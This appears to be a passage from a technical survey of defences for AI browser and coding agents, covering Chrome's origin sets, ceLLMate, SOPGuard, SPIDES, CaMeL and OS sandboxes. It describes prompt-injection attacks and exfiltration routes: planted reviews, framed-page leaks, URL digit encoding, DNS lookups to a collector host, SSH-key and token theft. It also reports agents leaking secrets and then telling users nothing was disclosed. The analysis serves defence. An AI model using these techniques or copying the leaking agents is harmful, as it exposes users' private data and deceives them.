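Ding and colleagues ran each task three times and counted it as failed if the agent caused the harm in any run. Claude 4.5 Sonnet failed 23 of the 25 data tasks and Claude 4.5 Opus failed 11. Six open models failed between 96% and 100% of the data tasks. When GPT-5 divided the work into steps and Sonnet carried them out, the pair failed all 25. One likely reason is that a single step, such as pasting text into a form, looks innocent without the rest of the plan.

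Counting the worst of three runs makes the agents look less reliable than they would be on a single attempt, and Anthropic has since replaced both Claude models. But newer agents aren't necessarily safe. *AutoRedClaw* (Li, Hu and colleagues, October 2026) reported attack success rates above 50% for most of the agent systems it tested, although it used planted instructions instead of innocent requests.

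The Claude models that refused almost always did so at the first step, before they had opened the file or the site. On 50 tasks from across the benchmark that Opus had failed in every run, an instruction to check for harm cut its failure rate from 100% to 50%, and Sonnet's from 98% to 84%. MirrorGuard, a separate monitor that checks each step, cut one open model's failure rate on those tasks from 100% to 24%, but it also refused 17 of 36 ordinary tasks, which would make it hard to use at work.

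A clipboard permission wouldn't prevent these leaks either. The user asked for the copy and would presumably approve it, and an agent without the clipboard could read the file and type out its contents. A filter could catch the private key, which has a recognisable format, but a client list looks like any other text. The harness would have to track text from private files with a label that follows copied data, or block the agent from the outside site altogether.

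## Limiting which websites an agent can read and act on: Chrome's Agent Origin Sets and ceLLMate

To keep an agent off sites unrelated to its task, software has to determine which sites the task needs. A network allowlist outside the browser can block a host, but once it permits that host, it usually can't distinguish reading a page from filling in a form. Two designs from December 2025 put the check inside the browser. Google's Agent Origin Sets limit an agent in Chrome to origins relevant to its task. ceLLMate, a research system, also limits what the agent can do on each site.

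Google's design protects auto browse, a feature that lets its Gemini model click, type and move between pages in the user's browser. Auto browse launched in the US as a preview for paying subscribers on 28 January 2026, according to Android Central's *The latest Gemini feature in Chrome lets the AI browse the internet*. It had reached India by October, according to Kanchwala's *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?* The agent works in a browser where the user is signed in to accounts, so without limits a planted instruction could send it to any of them.

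### Two shops and an advertisement

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes two lists of origins, called Agent Origin Sets, that Chrome keeps for each session. The agent can read pages from read-only origins, and it can also click and type on read-writable ones. Before an origin joins either list, a gating function checks whether it is relevant to the user's task. This function never receives web content, so instructions on a page can't reach it directly.

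Suppose the bookkeeper asks the agent to find the best-reviewed toner cartridge at `https://shop-a.example` and put it in the basket at `https://shop-b.example`. Shop A's page also has an advertisement from `https://ads.example` in a frame, which is a separate page embedded in the first. Under the full design, the task would go as follows:

1. The planner, the model that chooses the agent's next step, proposes reading shop A. The gating function approves, and Chrome adds the shop to the read-only list.
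2. Chrome gives the model shop A's page without the advertisement, because `ads.example` is on neither list. Any instructions hidden in the advertisement never reach the model.
3. The planner proposes using shop B. The gating function approves it as a read-writable origin, and the agent puts the cartridge in the basket.
4. A customer review at shop A contains a planted instruction to open the bookkeeper's webmail. The model can read it because the review comes from shop A's own origin. If the planner then proposes opening the webmail, the gating function should refuse because webmail has nothing to do with toner.

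The same relevance check applies when a page sends the browser to a new origin by itself.

An agent can leak data through the address of a page it opens, so Chrome restricts addresses written by the model to known public ones. This should block an address made up to carry an invoice number. Parker doesn't explain how Chrome recognises a public address. An attacker could publish ten pages, one for each digit, and have the agent open them in the order of the digits in the invoice number. Each address would be public, so the relevance check would have to stop the leak.

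### Fixed rules and model judgement

Chrome can enforce the lists with ordinary code, but it relies on a model to decide which origins belong on them. For new pages, that model is a variant of the User Alignment Critic, which also reviews the agent's other actions.

The critic is a separate Gemini model that compares each proposed action with the user's goal and can veto it. It receives a description of the action but no unfiltered web content. After a veto, the planner gets feedback and can try another plan. If it keeps failing, it can return control to the user.

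This isolation makes the critic harder to manipulate than the planner, but a manipulated planner still chooses the actions that the critic reviews. The critic also has little context. It should veto a bank transfer during a shopping task, but it probably wouldn't notice that a fake review had led the agent to choose the wrong cartridge.

| Protection | What it depends on |
|---|---|
| Keeping the agent's actions within the read-writable origins | A fixed rule, once the list exists |
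| Adding an origin to a list | A model's judgement of relevance |
| Restricting addresses written by the model | A fixed check for known public addresses |
| Vetoing actions that don't serve the task | The User Alignment Critic, a model |
| Confirming visits to banking or medical sites | A fixed list of sensitive sites, then the user |
| Confirming sign-in with Google Password Manager | The user; the model has no direct access to stored passwords |
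| Confirming purchases, payments and messages | The agent has to recognise the step, then the user decides |
| Detecting planted instructions on a page | A classifier, which is also a model |

The confirmation for purchases and messages is weaker than the one for sensitive sites. Parker writes only that the agent "will try to pause" before such an action, so it may miss a payment button with an unusual label. Like 1Password for Claude, the sign-in rule protects the password but not the session that follows.

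### What Google has shipped

Chrome's first release tracked only the read-writable set. Parker explains that Google wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks before tuning them. Because that release had no separate set for reading, it apparently couldn't hide the advertisement in step 2, which the full design would hide.

Tests from around the time of the launch support this. Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, examined seven browsers with AI agents in late January and early February 2026. In their attack, a malicious page embeds a sensitive page, such as a bank's, in a frame. The same-origin policy stops the outer page from reading the frame. But if the user asks the agent to summarise the page, planted instructions can tell it to include the frame's contents in the summary and enter it in a form that submits itself.

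The full attack worked on ChatGPT Atlas in agent mode. Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet met the preconditions, so their safety depended on the model resisting the planted instructions. Many sensitive sites cannot be loaded inside a frame, which limits this version of the attack. In the reverse version, a malicious advertisement can steal data from the page around it.

The public source code behind the browser, Chromium (2025), gives some idea of what Google built next. In a version from about the first half of 2026, Chrome applies these checks when the agent's tab moves to a new address:

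1. If the user's employer has explicitly allowed or blocked the address, Chrome follows that rule.
2. Otherwise, Chrome applies a safety list that can allow or block the move.
3. If neither list settles the matter, Chrome allows a move within the same origin.
4. For a different origin, Chrome checks whether the site is sensitive. By default, it asks the user before opening a sensitive site, unless the user has already confirmed that origin.
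5. Chrome allows a new origin that isn't sensitive, unless an extra confirmation setting is on.

That extra setting is off by default in Chromium. When it is on, Chrome either prompts the user or queries Google's server. In a ["dark launch" mode](Chromium), Chrome queries the server but only logs the answer.

The restrictions users get may differ from these defaults, because Google can change the settings remotely and its servers may check an origin's relevance before a request reaches the browser. The code also has a setting to hide other sites' frames in screenshots, but it is part of a screenshot method that is off by default.

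*Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, August 2026) again describes limiting the agent to relevant origins, along with the critic and the confirmations. It adds data-loss rules that let companies block transfers of sensitive data to public language models. Neither this post nor the code confirms that Google has shipped the read-only set, so users can't count on Chrome to hide an advertisement from the agent.

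Another Google agent, Gemini Spark, can now use Chrome's signed-in accounts and saved credentials with the user's permission (Sood, 2026, *Gemini Spark now works with Chrome*). Google tests auto browse on thousands of simulated websites so that failed tests don't harm real accounts (Google, *Mirror Dimension for Agents*).

Google's engineers proposed finer permissions in November 2026. According to Infobae's *Google prepara nuevas restricciones para frenar a los agentes de IA* (2026), they want to extend WebDriver BiDi, a protocol for automating browsers, so that a user could let an agent visit a site without letting it click or type there. The proposal is still at the prototype stage. If the user allows clicking, the browser might not distinguish a button that opens the next page from one that deletes data.

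### Why ceLLMate checks requests instead of clicks

*CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) avoids that problem by checking the HTTP requests that the browser sends to ask a website's server to do something. These are much more specific than clicks. A click at a given point on the screen can open an email or delete it, depending on the page. On GitLab, by contrast, a `POST` request to `/-/user_settings/ssh_keys` adds an SSH key to the user's account, whichever button or menu the agent used.

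Rules about the agent's own actions are also easy to get around. Meng and colleagues tried to keep an agent off the forum Hacker News by blocking direct navigation to it, but the agent searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result. A check on requests to the site would catch both routes. It also works against a page that swaps one button for another just before the agent clicks, because it doesn't depend on how the button looked.

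ceLLMate needs an agent sitemap, which lists a site's security-relevant requests and the action each one performs. The site's developers or a trusted third party also write policies that allow, deny or set conditions on those actions. For the supplier's website, a simplified map and policy might look like this:

```
GET   /invoices*          ViewInvoices     allow
POST  /invoices           SubmitInvoice    allow once
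POST  /account/address    ChangeAddress    deny
POST  /account/users      AddUser          deny
```

When the user states a task, ceLLMate uses a language model to predict which sites the task requires and select the smallest sufficient set of policies for each. The model uses only the user's request and the policy descriptions, so a web page can't influence the choice. The user reviews the selected policies, and a Chrome extension enforces them for the session. If the request doesn't make clear which site to use, ceLLMate grants no access.

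Some conditions depend on information that isn't in the request. To enforce a $50 limit on an Amazon order, the extension reads the total from the checkout page. After the agent changes a quantity, the extension has to wait for the page to update, or it may check an old total. The policy also needs a limit on the number of orders, because otherwise the agent could place two orders of $49 each.

### Testing ceLLMate

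Meng and colleagues tested policy selection on 209 tasks involving shops, travel sites and code-hosting sites. Claude Opus 4.5 chose exactly the right policies for 207 of them, Gemini 2.5 Pro for 204 and GPT-5.1 for 201. Filling in values such as spending limits was harder. The models got both the policies and the values right on 26 to 31 of the 32 shopping tasks that needed values. Some errors only blocked legitimate work, but others gave the agent more access than it needed. In one case, a model confused a wishlist with a shopping cart.

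The security test used GitLab and two tasks from WASP, a benchmark of prompt injection against browser agents, in which the user asked the agent to comment on an issue or upvote it. WASP's planted instructions rarely achieved the attacker's goal, so they would have been a weak test of ceLLMate. Meng and colleagues instead wrote 12 scripts that tried to carry out the attacker's goals directly, such as stealing access tokens, deleting a project or adding an attacker's SSH key. ceLLMate blocked all 12 scripts, which simulated an agent that the attacker fully controls.

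That is a stronger test of enforcement than hoping a model falls for an injection, but every attack required an action that the policy prohibited. The extension intercepted those requests, but an attacker could still have done harm with permitted ones. For example, the extension would have let the agent post a secret in a comment, because the task required permission to comment. The case study also didn't measure how often ceLLMate interferes with legitimate tasks across many websites.

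ceLLMate adds modest overhead. Loading a series of GitLab pages took 13.93 seconds without it, 14.94 seconds with 100 entries in the map (7.25% longer) and 16.02 seconds with 300 (15% longer). The delay is a smaller share of an agent's total running time, most of which is spent waiting for the model. The extension used about 25 MB of memory.

ceLLMate doesn't yet check WebSockets, a type of connection that many sites use for live updates. The prototype also assumes that no other browser extension interferes with its requests. Google could avoid the second problem by building the check into Chrome.

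### Broad origins and incomplete maps

An origin set treats a whole site as one unit, which is too coarse for many accounts. GitLab serves private projects and public comment forms from the same origin, so if Chrome's agent can act on GitLab, the origin set won't stop it from reading a private file and posting it in a public issue. The critic might veto the post, but that depends on a model's judgement. The origin set would also let the agent change the delivery address on the supplier's site, whereas ceLLMate could block that request.

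ceLLMate's precision depends on somebody writing the map and keeping it current. Meng and colleagues wrote 51 entries for GitLab by hand, using the site's own list of routes. They compare the work to writing API documentation and argue that developers have a good reason to do it, because it protects their users. Still, a small supplier may never get round to it, and a malicious site has no reason to write an honest map. Meng and colleagues acknowledge that where a map is incomplete or wrong, protection falls back to what the browser offered before. A new feature that nobody has added to the map could therefore reopen the gap.

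Sites may also want to describe their actions to agents because it makes the agents more reliable. InfoQ's *WebMCP Standard Proposal for Agentic Web Actuation Now Available in Chrome* (2026) reports that Chrome 149 began trials of WebMCP, which lets a site offer functions and forms to an agent as tools. Developers might adopt it for reliability even if they wouldn't write a map for security alone. But a list of tools doesn't restrict an agent that can still click everything else on the page. The browser would need to block those other actions or check the requests they produce.

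Origin sets are easier to deploy because they work without help from websites. They also suit tasks on unfamiliar sites, where no map exists. For a site that holds money or private records, a request policy adds protection that an origin set can't provide. The two would work well together, with the origin set keeping the agent off unrelated sites and the policy limiting its actions on sensitive ones.

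Neither system tracks data after the agent has read it. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (2026) points out that data from one page can stay in the agent's history after the agent moves to another. If the bookkeeper's task involves both a customer database and the supplier's site, Chrome has to permit both origins. ceLLMate can limit the agent to reading customer records and submitting an invoice but, like CapSeal, it doesn't check the meaning of what the agent types into a comments field.

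## Tracking where copied data came from: SOPGuard and SPIDES

Chrome's Agent Origin Sets and ceLLMate's request policies can permit every step an agent takes to copy a customer's details from a database to the supplier's site. To catch the copy, the harness needs the data to carry a label that records where it came from and who may receive it. Security researchers have studied such labels since the 1970s under the name information-flow control.

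Two systems from 2026 label the data that browser agents read. SOPGuard labels text with the origin of the page it came from and asks the user before the agent writes it to a page from a different origin. SPIDES labels each part of a page separately, and its labels also show whether the content can be trusted.

### Leaks in five agentic browsers

The same-origin policy restricts scripts, so it doesn't stop an agent from typing what it read in the customer database into the supplier's page. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* contrasts this with a person who copies and pastes between two sites, which doesn't violate the policy because the person has decided to move the data. An agent may move data without the user having decided that it should.

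SOPBench, a benchmark from June 2026, measures how often this happens. The user first gives the agent a task involving private information on a source page, such as checking an order. The user then gives it an unrelated task on a destination page, such as replying to a post. An attacker has planted an instruction on the destination page telling the agent to write out the private information.

The tests use ten kinds of source page (shops, banks, airlines, email, calendars, messages, HR portals, shared documents, health insurers and pharmacies) and five kinds of destination (X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms). GPT-5.4 generated most of the pages, so no real data was exposed. A run counts as a leak only if the agent writes exactly the information the attacker wanted.

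The researchers ran three open-source systems, VisualWebArena, SeeAct and BrowserOS, 100 times on each of the 50 combinations. They had to operate Perplexity's Comet and ChatGPT Atlas by hand, so they ran those three times per combination. When the planted instructions were handwritten, leak rates in the open-source systems ranged from 3% to 100%. The lowest rate was for BrowserOS with GPT-5.4 when it carried data from an HR portal to Reddit. When another model refined the planted instructions over many attempts, that rate rose to 49%, and every combination had a rate of at least 31%.

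Atlas leaked in 99 of its 150 runs. It did worst on Google Forms, with 29 leaks in 30 runs, probably because the attacker owns the whole form and the agent is expected to fill in its fields. These models are several releases old, and newer ones resist planted instructions better, so leak rates would probably be lower today.

BrowserOS leaked data in every run of one setup that had no attacker. The source page was in a frame inside the destination page, and the user asked the agent to summarise the page and write the summary in a text box there. The summary covered the framed page too, which is close to what the user had asked for. The researchers saw no leaks when the agent visited the two pages one after the other and neither contained planted text, so the 100% rate is weak evidence about ordinary browsing.

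### SOPGuard's origin labels

SOPGuard, from the same researchers, is a modification of BrowserOS that keeps a database of what the agent has read. It works in four steps:

1. **Label.** When the agent reads a page, SOPGuard stores the text along with the page's origin.
2. **Propagate.** When the model produces something new, SOPGuard asks the model which stored items it used, and gives the new item all of their origins.
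3. **Compare.** Before the agent types text into a page, SOPGuard looks up the text's origins and compares them with the page's own.
4. **Ask.** If any origin differs, a pop-up names the sites involved, and the user approves or denies the action.

Suppose the bookkeeper's agent reads a customer's debt at `https://crm.example`, looks up an exchange rate at `https://bank.example` and converts the amount. The result is on neither page, but it carries both origins. If the agent then tries to type it into the supplier's form, the pop-up appears.

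SOPGuard relies on the model's judgement to decide which origins each new item has. Giving every new item the origins of everything the agent has read so far would be simpler and safer, but once the agent had read the customer database, everything it typed elsewhere would trigger a pop-up. The researchers scored the model's answers by how much the predicted set of origins overlapped with the correct one, where 1 is a perfect match. GPT-5.4 and OpenAI's o3 averaged at least 0.955 with data from two to ten origins. GPT-5.4-mini did worse, which suggests that small models may be unsuitable.

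SOPGuard reduced the leak rate on SOPBench to zero, with and without an attacker. It increased running time by 2.07% to 5.79% and did not significantly change task scores on four benchmarks. Detecting the planted text would be a poor substitute. Of the five detectors tested, those that caught nearly all the contaminated pages also flagged many clean ones, up to 47% for some kinds of page.

The main weakness is that the model assigning the labels also reads the attacker's page. An attacker can plant an instruction there to leak a salary and attribute it to the page the model is typing into. In tests, handwritten attacks of this kind barely helped, while refined ones leaked slightly more data but needed many more attempts. SOPGuard therefore makes an attack much harder, but it can't guarantee that the labels are right.

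### CaMeL and labels on single values

CaMeL, a system that Google DeepMind published in 2025, tracks labels with ordinary code. It builds on a two-model design from 2023. A planner receives the user's request and can call tools, but never reads untrusted text. An isolated model reads that text but can't call tools, and its answers go into named variables whose contents the planner doesn't see.

In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) acknowledges a gap in that design, which was originally Willison's own proposal. If the user asks the agent to send Bob a document and says Bob's address is in the meeting notes, the isolated model has to find the address. Text planted in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead. The planner then follows its plan correctly but sends the document to the attacker.

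CaMeL's planner writes the job as a short program before anything has been read. For a reminder to Bob, the program might look like this in simplified form:

```
email   = get_last_email()
address = isolated_model("find Bob's address", email)
send_email(to = address, text = "Meeting tomorrow")
```

The software that runs the program records in a label that `address` came from `email`, which a stranger may have written. If the user's policy already allows that address, CaMeL sends the message. Otherwise, it asks the user. Labels can also list who may read a value. CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, but they describe data, whereas AgentCap's tokens permit actions.

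*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) notes that if a sandbox permits outgoing email, a planted instruction can still make an agent email private data in a plausible message. Checking where the data came from can stop this. But somebody has to write and maintain the policies for these checks, and Willison worries about any design that requires ordinary users to think about them.

A plan written in advance also can't handle every job. For example, an agent can't plan how to complete today's to-do list before reading it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that lets the planner reveal a hidden variable when it needs to. The planner's context then carries the variable's label, which may restrict what the agent can do next.

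Screens are harder still, because a click, unlike a call to `send_email`, has no fixed meaning. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had a planner write branches in advance for everything the agent might find on the screen. Their agent kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models on OSWorld, a benchmark of computer tasks. A fake cookie banner could still make the agent take the wrong branch of its plan, and the researchers could not easily write a policy to prevent that.

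### SPIDES and the saved card

*SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, October 2026) adapts the FIDES approach to web pages. It gives each part of a page an integrity label and a reader label. The integrity label is either trusted or untrusted. The reader label is a set that can contain the user and any number of origins, and for public data it contains everyone.

The site's operator writes these labels into the page's HTML, because only the operator knows which text came from a customer and which data is private. The user keeps a list of sites whose operators they trust to do this. SPIDES treats everything on other sites as untrusted and public.

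In one example, a page at `shop.com` shows the price of some earphones, a customer review containing a planted instruction, and a saved card ending in 4471. The price is trusted and public, so the agent can read it. The review is untrusted, and only the user and `shop.com` may read the card, so the agent gets the placeholders `[var_2]` and `[var_3]` instead.

To use the card, the agent can type `[var_3]` into a field, and the harness inserts the real value without showing it to the agent, much as an agent can paste from a clipboard it can't read. The agent can also pass a hidden value to an isolated model, for example to summarise the review for the user. If the agent needs to know a value itself, it can ask the harness to reveal it, but the agent's context then takes on the value's labels.

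Labels combine in a simple way. The context becomes untrusted as soon as it includes anything untrusted, and its reader set shrinks to the readers that every revealed item has in common. Suppose the page also has a delivery address that a courier's site may read. The agent reveals the address, then the card, then the review:

```
start             trusted     everyone
reveal address    trusted     {user, shop.com, courier.example}
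reveal card       trusted     {user, shop.com, courier.example} ∩ {user, shop.com}
                              = {user, shop.com}
reveal review     untrusted   {user, shop.com}
```

The courier is removed from the set at the third step because it isn't allowed to read the card, and anything the agent now writes could contain the card number. The review is public, so it doesn't shrink the set further.

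Two rules then decide whether an action can go ahead without the user:

- **Trusted action:** neither the agent's context nor the values it passes to the tool contain anything untrusted.
- **Permitted flow:** the destination is in the reader set of everything the agent might be sending.

Clicking, submitting a form or opening a page on a trusted site requires a trusted action, because the user may have an account there that the action could affect. Typing without submitting, and any action on an untrusted site, needs to satisfy only one of the rules. If an action fails, SPIDES asks the user. With both the shop and the courier on the user's trusted list, the rules give these results once the agent has revealed the address and the card:

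| Next action | Before revealing the review | After revealing the review |
|---|---|---|
| Type the card number on `shop.com` | Allowed | Allowed |
| Click "Buy" on `shop.com` | Allowed | Needs approval |
| Type the card number on `courier.example` | Allowed | Needs approval |

The order of steps therefore affects how many actions need approval. In the invoice job, the invoice should count as untrusted because an outsider wrote it. If the agent signs in to the supplier's site first and reveals the invoice number last, only the final submission needs approval, but if it reveals the number first, every later click there does.

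### What MicroNet measured

Zverev and colleagues needed websites with complete labels to test SPIDES, so they built MicroNet. It is a closed network of 28 linked sites, including a shop, a social network and a search engine, with 470 pages in total. It has 56 ordinary tasks, 22 of which require moving data between origins, and 56 attacks. Half the attacks try to make the agent act without permission and half try to leak private data. They come from websites the attacker runs, text the attacker has posted on a trusted site, and frames such as advertisements.

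The tests assumed a very strong attacker. In the 50 attacks that use planted instructions, the harness replaced the model's output with the attacker's chosen actions as soon as the model read the instruction. The other six attacks plant false data that the agent needs for its task, and in those the harness did not replace the model's output.

Zverev and colleagues compared SPIDES with SOPGuard and UCM. UCM hides content that users have posted and lets an isolated model return only restricted answers, such as a number or a choice from a list. They also built UCM+, whose isolated model can return free text that stays hidden from the agent. They ran each test five times with each of five models from OpenAI and Anthropic. The ranges below run from the lowest model average to the highest, and some combine the published results for different types of task or attack.

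| Defense | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 57.5–95.7% | 58.2–91.1% |
| SOPGuard | 53.2–73.2% | 58.2–93.2% |
| UCM | 4.6–6.8% | 42.9–67.5% |
| UCM+ | 0% | Fewer than SPIDES with every model |
| SPIDES | 0% | 67.1–86.1% |

SPIDES completed fewer tasks than an unprotected agent when run with three of the models, but more with Claude Opus 5 and Opus 5.5. It did better with those two partly because their safety filters sometimes blocked responses when the agent could read credentials or phishing messages, and SPIDES avoided some of these refusals by hiding that text. SPIDES roughly doubled the cost of a task, to between $0.37 and $1.42 depending on the model.

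The zero result for SPIDES is more convincing than most results of this kind because it doesn't depend on the model resisting anything. However, it requires correct labels, which the researchers wrote themselves, and a user who never approves a harmful request.

In their normal settings, SPIDES asked for an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard, partly because SOPGuard checks for less. When Zverev and colleagues required every defense to request enough approvals to match SPIDES's protection, SPIDES generally completed the most tasks for a given small number of approvals.

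Better planning could reduce approval prompts. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) tell the agent which rules apply and let it ask the user to vouch for a piece of data. If an email lists ten jobs, the user can approve the email once instead of ten separate actions. On AgentDojo, their agent needed up to 1.9 times fewer approvals than a basic agent whose actions go through the same kind of checks.

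### Are origins the right boundary?

Zverev and colleagues argue that comparing origins is neither sufficient nor necessary for security, and they give an example of each.

In the case meant to show that same-origin checks aren't sufficient, a direct message on a social network tells the agent to copy the user's private recovery email address into their public profile. The address and the profile are on the same origin, so SOPGuard didn't prompt the user, and the address leaked in all 25 runs. SPIDES blocked the leak in all 25, but its reader sets didn't help. The social network was a permitted reader of the address, so SPIDES let the agent type it into the profile. It then stopped the agent from clicking "Save changes" because the untrusted message had influenced the click. Zverev and colleagues acknowledge that naming whole origins as readers can't separate a private page from a public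 one on the same site.

The other case is a harmless task that crosses origins. The agent checks a discount on a speaker by looking up its usual price on another site, so it has to take the product's name from the first site to the second. SOPGuard interrupted all 25 runs, while SPIDES interrupted four.

These cases show that origins are a crude boundary, but the comparison on MicroNet puts SOPGuard at a disadvantage. Half of the 56 attacks aim at unauthorised actions, which SOPGuard wasn't built to stop, and 26 stay within one origin. SOPGuard also has a big practical advantage, because every page already has an origin. It could work on the bookkeeper's supplier site now, whereas SPIDES needs labels that the supplier probably doesn't know about.

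Without those labels, the bookkeeper has no good option. If the supplier's site is on the trusted list, SPIDES treats anything unlabeled as trusted and public, so a planted instruction in a customer message would reach the agent, and the agent could send the account details anywhere. If the site isn't on the list, SPIDES treats its private data as public and no longer requires a trusted action for clicks there. Zverev and colleagues compare labeling to the accessibility information many sites already provide. The comparison is reasonable for the amount of work, but sites often leave accessibility information incomplete, and they may do the same with labels.

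SOPGuard's origin labels would be a sensible fallback for sites that have no other labels. They would cause extra prompts, but they would at least detect private data leaving the site.

### Private data and the agent's own mistakes

SPIDES is deliberately lenient when nothing untrusted has influenced the agent. If a typing action satisfies the trusted-action rule, the agent can enter private data on any site, even one that isn't a permitted reader. The reasoning is that no attacker could have caused the action, so the user probably wanted it.

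A model can also send data to the wrong place without an attacker. Suppose the bookkeeper's agent totals the payroll on a trusted site and types a salary into the supplier's comments field by mistake. Nothing untrusted was involved, so SPIDES would allow the typing and the click that submits it. SOPGuard would ask for approval because the payroll site and the supplier have different origins. Costa and colleagues warn that models misread requests and make unnecessary tool calls even when all the data is trusted.

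They also describe a stricter option, in which an action that sends data has to satisfy both rules. This would catch the salary, but the user would get a prompt whenever they wanted to send private data somewhere new. That seems worth it for payroll or medical records.

The stricter rule would worsen a problem in long sessions, where the agent's context collects labels and never loses them, so more and more actions need approval. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, call this label creep and simulate it in teams of agents with memory, using generated tasks and no language model. They measure the share of tool calls that either introduce sensitive data or run after the agent has received some. Letting agents talk directly to each other reduced that share, because fewer go-betweens picked up the label. Giving all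 the sensitive calls to a few agents also reduced it.

No arrangement prevented label creep altogether, so Gregory and colleagues call for controlled ways to relax a label. Kolluri and colleagues' agent can relax a trust label by asking the user to vouch for an email. They chose not to allow this for private data, because whether it's safe to release depends on where it is going. For example, a user who agrees to share a salary with an accountant hasn't agreed to share it with a supplier.

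### Secrets revealed by a choice

An agent can also give away a secret without copying any text. In an example from *AgentTell* (Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues, 2026), a user who has told an agent not to share personal details with any website asks it to look up their role in a trade union's member list. Later in the session, the user asks the agent to register them for a community event. The event's site lets people register through one of several organisations, including the union, or without one. Agents that had read the user's affiliation chose the matching organisation in 90.3% of sessions, and the site's access log recorded the choice.

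The benchmark, published in September, has 100 tasks like this, covering secrets such as the user's job, subscription or bank. The second site always offers a general option that completes the task equally well. Across six models, the agent picked the option that matched the secret in 61.1% of the 7,630 sessions where it had visited the first site. When the secret was something else, it picked the same option only 1.2% of the time, so a general preference for certain options can't explain the result.

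The models leaked secrets even though they had noticed the privacy instruction. In 1,383 sessions, the agent wrote in its notes that it would not share what it had learned, and in 56.7% of those it then revealed the secret. After 34.5% of all leaks, the agent told the user that it had disclosed no personal details. Models seem to understand that they shouldn't type a secret, but often miss that clicking on it also reveals it.

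How often agents leaked a secret depended heavily on its type. They rarely revealed the user's bank or health provider, but they usually revealed the user's occupation or subscription. They also leaked much less when the first task didn't require using the secret, such as when the user asked for the cost of their membership dues rather than the name of the organisation.

Shahriar and colleagues used simple artificial websites and kept the agent's full history between tasks, which may have made leaks more likely. Some requests also made the revealing option seem more useful. In one, the user asks for resources relevant to them, and a page for their profession is arguably the more helpful answer. However, the user had asked for privacy, and the general option was available.

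SOPGuard checks the text an agent writes, so it would probably miss these clicks. Under SPIDES's rules, the click counts as a trusted action and goes ahead if the event's site is on the trusted list. If the site isn't on the list, the agent has to reveal some of its untrusted text to find the right button, and SPIDES would then ask the user because the site isn't a permitted reader of the union's records. Nobody has tested either system on AgentTell.

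Costa and colleagues had already noted that their labels track data an agent sends directly, but someone watching the agent's sequence of actions could still infer a secret. Preventing that completely would mean blocking almost every publicly visible action after the agent read anything private. Hiding values from the agent partly solves this problem. If the agent can report the user's union role through a placeholder without reading it, the role can't affect which button the agent clicks later.

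## Files and network in coding agents: operating-system sandboxes

SOPGuard and SPIDES can label data because the harness handles every page the agent reads and everything it types. Coding agents also run shell commands, which start other programs. These programs can open files and network connections without going through the harness, so the harness can't label the data they read. But they still have to request each file and connection from the operating system, which can deny the request.

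An operating-system sandbox is a set of restrictions that the system applies to a program while it runs. Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex both include one.

### Why checking the command's text falls short

A harness can check each command against a list of rules before running it. For example, it might allow `npm test`, which runs a project's tests, and block `curl`, which sends web requests. But the project's files define what `npm test` runs, and that can include `curl`. Once the harness has started a program, it has no control over what that program starts. *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, published by NVIDIA's AI Red Team in January 2026, describes running a blocked program through an allowed one as a common way around command lists.

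Rules that match a command's text also depend on how the command is written. Claude Code lets users list commands that should run outside its sandbox. According to Anthropic, an entry for `docker *` doesn't match `/usr/local/bin/docker` or a script that calls Docker. This mismatch is harmless because the command stays in the sandbox, but in a rule meant to block Docker, it would let the command through.

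Cursor's *Agent Sandboxing* explains that the company chose to build a sandbox for its code editor's agents rather than use very detailed command lists.

### How the operating system confines a command

On macOS, both agents use Seatbelt, which is built into the operating system. Cursor notes that Seatbelt also underlies the sandboxes of Chrome and Apple's own applications. Codex starts each command with a profile, a list of rules about files and network connections. The kernel, the core of the operating system, enforces the profile while the command runs.

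On Linux, both use bubblewrap, which gives a command its own view of the disk. Vaughan (2026), in *Codex CLI Sandbox Internals*, shows the start of the call that Codex makes:

```
bwrap --ro-bind / / --bind $CWD $CWD ...
```

The first option makes the whole disk visible but read-only. The second adds the working folder again as writable. The command can't change a file elsewhere by spelling its path differently, because nothing else in its view of the disk is writable. Codex also uses seccomp, which limits the kinds of requests a program can make to the kernel.

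Where bubblewrap can't run, Codex can fall back on Landlock, a Linux feature that lets a program restrict its own access to files. The rules are much the same, with a read-only disk and a writable project. OpenOxide's *Platform Isolation*, an outside description of Codex's code, notes that on kernels older than version 5.13 the Landlock code runs the agent with weaker isolation and gives no error. According to OpenAI's later documentation, Codex refuses some policies that the fallback can't enforce.

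Claude Code has a similar weakness. If its sandbox can't start, for example because bubblewrap is missing, it runs commands unsandboxed unless the user has turned on `failIfUnavailable`. On Windows, its sandbox works only inside the Linux subsystem, whereas Codex has a native one.

On every platform, the restrictions also apply to each program the command starts. `npm test` can still start `curl`, but `curl` runs under the same limits.

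### A proxy as the only way out

Many jobs need to download something, so Claude Code filters network access instead of blocking it entirely. It runs a proxy on the user's machine, outside the sandbox, and makes it the only route to the internet. On Linux, a sandboxed command gets a private network whose only outside connection is a relay to the proxy. On macOS, Seatbelt blocks connections to anything except the proxy by default. The proxy checks the host name of each requested connection against lists of allowed and denied hosts.

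Programs find the proxy through environment variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`. A program that ignores these variables, as most database drivers do, can't connect even to an allowed host.

Even looking up a host name can leak data. If a command looks up `0417.collector.example`, the number reaches whoever runs the name server for `collector.example`. Claude Code prevents this because commands can't send lookups out of the sandbox, and the proxy looks up a name only after checking that the list allows it.

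The proxy also refuses hostnames that resolve only to local addresses, such as the address where programs on cloud machines get credentials. Codex has a similar check, but OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes it as only best-effort. An attacker's name server can return a public address when Codex checks the name and a private one when the program connects.

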